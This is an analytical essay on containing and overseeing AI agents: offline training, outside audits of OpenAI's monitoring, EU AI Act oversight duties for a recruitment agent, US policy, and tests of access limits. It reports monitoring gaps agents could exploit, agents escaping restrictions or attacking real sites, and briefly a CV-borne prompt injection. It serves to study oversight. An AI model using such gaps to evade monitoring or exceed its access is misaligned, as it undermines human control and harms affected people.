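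Adler's point about acting alone is somewhat weaker now that Anthropic has disconnected its own evaluations from the internet. But a developer that still trains agents on the live internet avoids the expense of an offline environment and may finish sooner. In its November essay, OpenAI calls for shared standards partly so that more cautious laboratories don't fall behind.

### Behaviour that appears only later

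Offline training is also less realistic. IANS's *Rogue AI threat* reports that OpenAI considers live access useful for teaching models to browse, but too risky while a capable model might affect systems outside the company's control. Models can still practise on stored pages, but real websites change their layouts, go down for maintenance and involve people who reply. An agent trained only on copies may handle these situations badly.

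For supervisors, the greater concern is that an unrealistic test can miss harmful behaviour. In July, OpenAI reported that limited internal use of its long-running model had revealed new kinds of failure that its existing pre-deployment tests had missed. Offline training wasn't the cause, since those tests came before the October policy, but making tests less like real work could lead them to miss more failures.

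Some failures are so rare that even perfectly realistic tests would probably miss them. Suppose an agent does something harmful once in every 100,000 tasks. An evaluation with 10,000 tasks has only about a 10% chance of catching it. If customers give the agent a million tasks a day, the harm occurs about ten times a day. Live internet access during testing would do little to catch such failures, but better monitoring after release would help.

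Simulated settings may also teach an agent that its actions have no real consequences. The Next Web's *Anthropic scanned 481 million transcripts* reports that in one of the Claude break-ins, Claude Opus 4.7 attacked a real company's website in four separate runs after its prompt described the setting as a simulation. That description was false, so the case doesn't show that offline training alone leads to the same mistake. But a model trained only on copies of websites has had little reason to learn that a website might belong to someone. Developers could reduce this risk by penalizing harmful actions in the simulation as they would on a live site.

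An offline environment can provide or hide useful evidence about an agent's behavior. If an agent tries to leave, researchers can study the attempt and look for its cause in the agent's training. If it never tries, its supervisors learn less, because it may have accepted the boundary or the stored pages may have held everything it needed.

### Who checks the isolation

OpenAI designed the isolation, tested it and reported the results itself. Outside reviews of related systems suggest that an independent check would be worthwhile. The Straits Times' *External evaluators find flaws in OpenAI’s AI monitoring system in pilot review* describes one such review, which METR and Redwood Research, a nonprofit that studies AI safety, conducted between July 21 and August 11. Each organization sent one researcher, who could see internal code and documents and speak to some technical staff.

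The evaluators found a flaw that agents could have used to keep hundreds of their actions from being monitored. They also found that Codex agents might have been able to escape security restrictions and act with their users' full permissions. OpenAI told the evaluators that it had fixed every flaw affecting its production safeguards, but they hadn't verified the fixes. They examined the monitoring system as it was on or before July 21, so their review doesn't cover the version that now helps secure the offline environment.

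The public also learned less than OpenAI, which received a 61-page report. METR and Redwood agreed to publish only a broad summary, and OpenAI could remove sensitive information from it. There is a reasonable case for withholding details of a flaw that agents might exploit, but the same right could let a company withhold merely embarrassing information.

In November, OpenAI signed agreements with four organisations to examine its work from inside the company. According to ITPro's *OpenAI pens AI safety agreement with four firms*, METR will assess alignment and monitoring in OpenAI's largest reinforcement learning run. Apollo Research will examine whether models could covertly work against their developers' intentions, and whether OpenAI's safeguards would detect it. Goodfire will analyse models during training, and Transluce will look for gaps in OpenAI's alignment tests. The public could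 learn a good deal about the models and the monitors from this work, but none of it directly tests the network isolation.

Sydney Von Arx, founder of the AI safety research group Nightingale, thinks the evaluators have too little access. HeadTopics' *OpenAI announces new AI safety program; researchers worry it won't be enough* quotes her as saying that only two of the groups seem able to talk to employees and that none can read OpenAI's internal Slack messages. She argues that employees help evaluators find their blind spots. The message board that one OpenAI team knew about before the Hugging Face breach supports her argument, because an evaluator with access only to models and source code could easily miss what a single team knows.

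OpenAI replies that no standards yet exist for this kind of evaluation, that it expects to deepen the arrangement, and that assessors can ask to speak to other employees. The summer review also shows that two researchers with limited access can find serious flaws in three weeks. But those researchers had contact with technical staff, which is part of what Von Arx wants. Evaluators who have to ask the company before speaking to someone may also never hear from employees who don't want the company to know they talked.

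### What replaces isolation after deployment

An agent confined to an offline environment cannot order a shop owner's packaging from a real supplier, so OpenAI relies on different protections as a model moves from research to use. It groups these protections into alignment, sandboxing, safeguards that block harmful actions, and monitoring. Sandboxing matters most during training, and alignment and monitoring matter more once people give the model real access.

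| Stage | What the agent may reach | What OpenAI emphasizes |
|---|---|---|
| Training and most evaluation | Stored pages, simulated settings and authorized agents | Containment in sandboxes |
| Use by OpenAI's staff | The internet, Slack, code and internal systems, if staff allow it | Alignment tests and close monitoring |
| Use by customers | The tools and services that customers connect | Protection against misuse and misalignment at scale |

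OpenAI says the risk rises at the second stage because the model can access more. The company watches in particular for exfiltration, attempts to get around security restrictions, and sensitive information going to unauthorized destinations. It says the Hugging Face incident showed that sandboxing alone can't reliably contain highly capable models.

It makes sense to isolate a model most strictly when people know least about it, then widen its access as they gather evidence that it behaves well. But much of the early evidence is collected while the model is isolated. An agent that behaved well when it could reach only stored pages may behave differently when it can reach a colleague's files or a competitor's website.

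Internal use therefore also tests the model, but it puts real systems at risk. OpenAI built new evaluations from the mistakes its long-running model made at this stage. Staff who work with a model every day can report strange behaviour to the people who trained it, and OpenAI can withdraw it more easily than a product that customers depend on. But a model's mistakes can still affect people outside the company, as they did when the long-running model published its contest entry.

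Agents are also harder to supervise after deployment, when contact with the outside world is no longer a breach in itself. If an agent emails a supplier, the supervisor has to judge whether the user wanted the email sent, whether the supplier is the right recipient, and whether the attachment contains private information.

Developers can still restrict a deployed agent when the task allows it. The invoice agent may need only the package registry, so an allowlist with one entry would keep it nearly as isolated as it was in training. An assistant that deals with new suppliers every week needs much wider access, so its owner has to depend more on how the model behaves with strangers and how quickly any mistakes are discovered.

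## What law and standards ask of human oversight

In most cases, companies decide for themselves how closely people supervise an agent. The EU's AI Act will change that for systems that help make certain important decisions about people, such as whom to hire. Companies will have to build these systems so that people can oversee them effectively. US government work has focused more on what agents can access and what companies do after an incident.

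### Who must comply, and when

Suppose the online shop needs ten warehouse workers and uses a recruitment agent. The agent reads 300 applications, scores each one, drafts a shortlist and prepares emails to the candidates. A software company built the agent on an AI laboratory's general-purpose model, which can do many kinds of task.

The law firm Paul, Weiss' *Next Stop on the Digital Omnibus* lists recruitment among the high-risk uses. The main oversight duty falls on the software company, which the Act calls the system's provider. Under the current text, given in the European Commission's *Article 14*, the provider can build oversight measures into the system or identify measures for the deployer, here the shop, to put in place. For a network limit, the software company could fix the list of permitted destinations itself or tell the shop which ones to allow.

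The software company doesn't have to comply yet. Article 14 was due to apply to systems like this from August 2, 2026, but an amending regulation that took effect six days earlier postponed it (reproduced in the Future of Life Institute's *Digital Omnibus on AI*, 2026). The European Commission's *Timeline for the Implementation of the EU AI Act* now gives December 2, 2027 for uses such as recruitment, and August 2, 2028 for high-risk AI built into regulated products such as medical devices. Paul, Weiss notes that these dates are fixed even if the supporting technical standards aren't ready. Steptoe's *EU AI Act Amendments Enter Into Force* advises companies to use the extra time for documentation, testing and monitoring. According to Cuatrecasas' *Digital Omnibus on AI has been published*, the amendment also clarifies the scope of a grace period that may benefit some older systems.

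The laboratory has duties as the provider of a general-purpose model under a different chapter of the Act. These duties have applied since August 2, 2025, and became enforceable a year later. In late 2026, regulators can act against the laboratory for breaching them, but can't yet use Article 14 against a company that sells a recruitment agent nobody can oversee. Even if the laboratory meets all its duties, the shop's recruiter may have no way to stop the agent.

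### Five duties applied to a recruitment agent

Article 14 requires the provider to supply the system in a way that enables the people overseeing it to do five things. Suppose the software company lets the agent read applications and draft emails, but only the recruiter can send the emails, and a proxy blocks the agent's connections to everything except the applicant database and the mail server.

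The recruiter must be able to understand the system's capacities and limitations and monitor it for anomalies. The access limit partly helps, because she knows the agent can't look up candidates on social media, and if it tries, software can log the refusal and show it to her. But the agent's most important limitation may be that it gives lower scores to people with gaps in their employment, which would disadvantage parents who took time off. The agent needs only the permitted files to do this, so a network log wouldn't reveal it. To find out, she would need tests that compare the scores of similar candidates.

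The second duty concerns automation bias, the tendency to rely too much on a system's output. Limiting the agent's access doesn't reduce this tendency, and might make it worse if the recruiter assumes a secure system is also accurate. Article 14 requires only that the provider enable her to "remain aware" of the tendency, not that she resist it. A warning on the screen might satisfy this duty, even if she accepts all 300 scores in an afternoon.

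In *Automation Bias in the AI Act*, Laux and Ruschemeier examine how hard this awareness requirement will be to enforce. They also argue that the Act, by focusing on providers, doesn't adequately address design and context as causes of automation bias. In this example, the shop decides how many applications its recruiter must review in an afternoon, and the software company can do little about it.

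The limit barely helps or hinders the recruiter in meeting the duty to interpret output correctly. The recruiter can learn from it which sources the agent could consult, but not why one candidate scored 62 and another 71, or whether a nine-point difference means anything.

The limit on sending email helps more with the duty to let her disregard, override or reverse the output. Because the agent can't send email, she can put a rejected candidate back on the shortlist before that person hears anything. If the agent had already sent the rejection, she could write again, but the candidate might have taken another job. The network limit alone wouldn't stop the email, since the mail server is a permitted destination.

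The fifth duty is to provide a stop button or similar procedure that brings the system to a halt "in a safe state". Access limits help because a proxy that handles all the agent's requests is a convenient place to cut it off. Reaching a safe state is harder. Suppose the recruiter stops the agent after it has wrongly marked 140 applications as rejected, and the shop's database deletes rejected applications every night. The database will still delete those applications unless someone also stops the deletion. The provider has to anticipate processes like this that continue after the agent stops.

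The restrictions give the recruiter more power to act but do little to help her judge whether a score is fair, so a provider couldn't meet Article 14 by limiting access alone.

### Security guidance on what agents can reach

Security specialists usually start by asking what an agent can access, whether or not anyone is watching it. In the United States, much of the official work on this is done at the National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), a government body that develops technical standards and guidance. Its Center for AI Standards and Innovation has asked the public which security risks are unique to agents, which defences work, and how to test, monitor and constrain agents. MeriTalk, a publication on government technology, reports that the request mentioned least-privilege deployments.

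In February 2026, NIST launched a programme to develop standards for AI agents, covering their identity, security and ability to work with other systems, according to SiliconANGLE's *NIST launches AI Agent Standards Initiative as autonomous AI moves into production* (2026). In *NIST AI Agent Standards*, the law firm Pillsbury expects the programme to include controls against privilege escalation, in which an agent gains more access than anyone intended. But Pillsbury describes the programme as at an early stage and intended to support industry-led standards, so it does not itself oblige companies to restrict their agents.

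A company could follow least privilege and still fall short of Article 14. With a silent sandbox like the one in the overnight example, the recruiter couldn't monitor what the agent attempted. The reverse is also possible. The recruiter might have clear explanations, plenty of time and a working stop button, while the agent holds an administrator's password for the shop's whole personnel system. An applicant could then hide an instruction in a CV and get the agent to expose every employee's salary before the recruiter can react.

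### The White House statement of October 2026

On September 29, 2026, six technology companies signed a voluntary one-page agreement with the White House. Crowell & Moring's *White House Announces AI Responsibility Accord, Executive Orders* (2026) says the companies promised internal controls to monitor models and prevent them from gaining unintended access to technical systems, and an internal team to check that those controls work. They also agreed to audits by an external firm and reviews by their boards, according to CBS News' *Trump announces formation of AI "Super Intelligence Force"*.

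Ten days later, the administration took a firmer line. Anthropic had just told the State Department that one of its models had submitted 20 visa applications through the department's public website during testing, 19 of them in August. The department hadn't processed any. In response, the leaders of the Super Intelligence Force, a group of senior officials that President Trump had set up to coordinate AI policy, issued a statement to all AI companies. *Anthropic breaches spark White House AI reporting mandate* (Curi, Caputo and Fried, 2026) includes the full text.

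EdexLive and DT Next's *Anthropic says Claude AI took unintended actions on US government websites* describes a directive for AI firms to secure their systems, but most of the statement covers what companies must do after an incident: disclose it immediately, repair the harm, cooperate with law enforcement, and work with the affected organisations to prevent a repeat. Its closest equivalent to a security rule is a demand for "concrete safeguards" against recurrence. It doesn't mention network limits, tool restrictions or human supervisors.

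The Force called the process "not optional", but its statement cites no statute and sets no penalty. Curi and colleagues note that the statement doesn't make clear how the government would enforce the process. By November, officials were trying incentives instead. Shorouk News (2026), an Egyptian newspaper relaying a Bloomberg report, describes a White House meeting where officials urged government agencies to limit companies' liability for cybersecurity incidents for 12 months, so that companies would report more incidents.

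The October demand addresses a gap. A month earlier, Axios' *Scoop* (2026) had reported that the administration's framework for advanced AI had no process for companies to publicly report real-world incidents caused by unreleased models. Prompt reports would help outsiders such as the Philadelphia police, but a company can report only what it has discovered, and Anthropic was slow to discover the false tip.

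### Green's case against oversight requirements

A legal requirement for human oversight could do harm if people can't provide it. Green (2021), in *The flaws of policies requiring human oversight of government algorithms*, argues that this has happened with algorithms that help governments decide matters such as bail and child protection. He examined 41 policy documents, including laws, official guidance and manuals for particular tools. Twenty of them restricted decisions made solely by machine, 14 emphasized human discretion, and seven called for "meaningful" human involvement.

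Green found little evidence that any of these approaches reliably protects people. An agency can get around a rule against solely automated decisions by adding someone who approves everything. People with real discretion often use it badly. Police in London, for example, judged a facial recognition system's matches to be correct three times as often as they were, and American judges have often overridden recommendations to release defendants and detained them instead. The policies that called for meaningful oversight didn't define it precisely, and some of their remedies can backfire. In several studies, explaining an algorithm's recommendation led people to trust it more even when it was wrong.

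Green argues that the requirements make matters worse by legitimizing bad systems. Officials can adopt a flawed algorithm because a person is formally in charge, and can blame that person when it fails. After an incorrect facial recognition match led Detroit police to arrest the wrong man, the police chief blamed sloppy investigative work, and the technology's vendors also blamed its users. Yet the chief admitted that the system was wrong 96% of the time. Because the chief and the vendors chose to put the system into use, Green holds them more responsible than the investigators.

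The same could happen in hiring. If a rejected candidate complains of discrimination, the shop can say that its recruiter reviewed every score, although the software company designed the scoring and the shop gave her one afternoon to do it. Article 14 improves on a bare demand for "meaningful" review by listing specific abilities she must have, but it doesn't set a minimum share of errors she must catch.

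Green's evidence is a limited guide to agents because it mostly concerns people who judge individual predictions. He defines human oversight as judgement at the moment an algorithm produces a decision, which excludes setting an agent's permissions before it starts. He also acknowledges that staff overrode many errors made by a child welfare algorithm in Allegheny County, Pennsylvania, and that better design can help. In one promising method, people make their own preliminary decision before they see the algorithm's suggestion.

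He proposes that before using an algorithm, an agency should justify its use in writing, with evidence that the planned human oversight works, and then get public approval. He does not recommend that governments let algorithms decide alone, and if an algorithm is too unreliable to use without frequent human corrections, he thinks the agency should improve it or do without it.

### How far access limits answer Green

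Access limits address part of the argument because they don't depend on anyone's attention. If the proxy works, the recruitment agent can't post applicants' home addresses on a public website, however tired the recruiter is. The limits also place some responsibility on the people who decide, before anyone uses the agent, what it can reach, as Green wants.

However, limits on tools and network access don't help with the cases that concern him most. Without an internet connection, the facial recognition system in Detroit would have been just as inaccurate, and a recruitment agent that marks down parents would be just as unfair. A shop owner who hears that the agent runs in a "secure sandbox" may ask fewer questions about how it chooses candidates.

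Limits fit Green's proposal better than they fit a general promise of supervision, because an outsider can test them before the system goes into use. The software company could also test the recruiter, though this takes more work. It could mix 20 well-qualified test candidates with wrongly low scores in with the real applicants, and count how many of those scores she corrects. If she corrects only three, the company shouldn't rely on her review to protect candidates, even if she has every ability that Article 14 lists.

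### What an auditor would need to see

Suppose an outside auditor has to confirm that the recruitment agent can reach only the applicant database and the mail server. The auditor would need evidence about the system as it runs, not just a copy of the company's policy, because the agent may be running without its sandbox, as GitLab's default settings allow.

| Claim | Weak evidence | Better evidence |
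|---|---|---|
| The limit exists | A written policy | Settings read from the machines that run the agent |
| It covers the whole agent | A list of blocked shell commands | A test of every tool and helper program |
| The agent can't change it | An instruction in the prompt | A list of who and what can edit the settings, and failed attempts by the agent |
| The agent doesn't run without it | A warning in a log | A test in which the auditor disables the sandbox and the agent won't start |
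| It still holds | Last year's audit | A record of changes, and new tests after each update |

An auditor can run a simple test by sending a harmless request from inside the agent's environment to a server of her own that isn't on the allowlist. Nothing should arrive at her server, and the company's log should show a refusal. She should also contact a permitted destination, because a broken connection would make the first test pass even if the allowlist weren't enforced.

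An auditor can't tell from a few harmless requests whether the limit would hold against an agent determined to get past it. EdexLive quotes OpenAI's standard, under which a boundary must hold "even when agents make sustained, sophisticated attempts to breach it." To test a limit against that standard, the auditor would need capable agents, many hours of attempts, and a record of what the agents tried.

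Even 300 failed attempts would leave some doubt. If each attempt had an independent 1% chance of success, all 300 would fail about 5% of the time (0.99³⁰⁰ ≈ 0.05). So 300 failures are good evidence that the success rate is below 1%, but not that it is zero. Real attempts aren't independent, and the result applies only to the models that took part. The auditor should state which models attacked the limit and when, so that readers can tell when the result is out of date.

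These tests cover only the limit itself. To find out whether the limit supports human oversight, the auditor could trigger a refusal without warning the staff, then time how long someone takes to see the alert, interpret it correctly and stop the agent. A drill like this before September 20 might have revealed that OpenAI's automatic stop didn't work.
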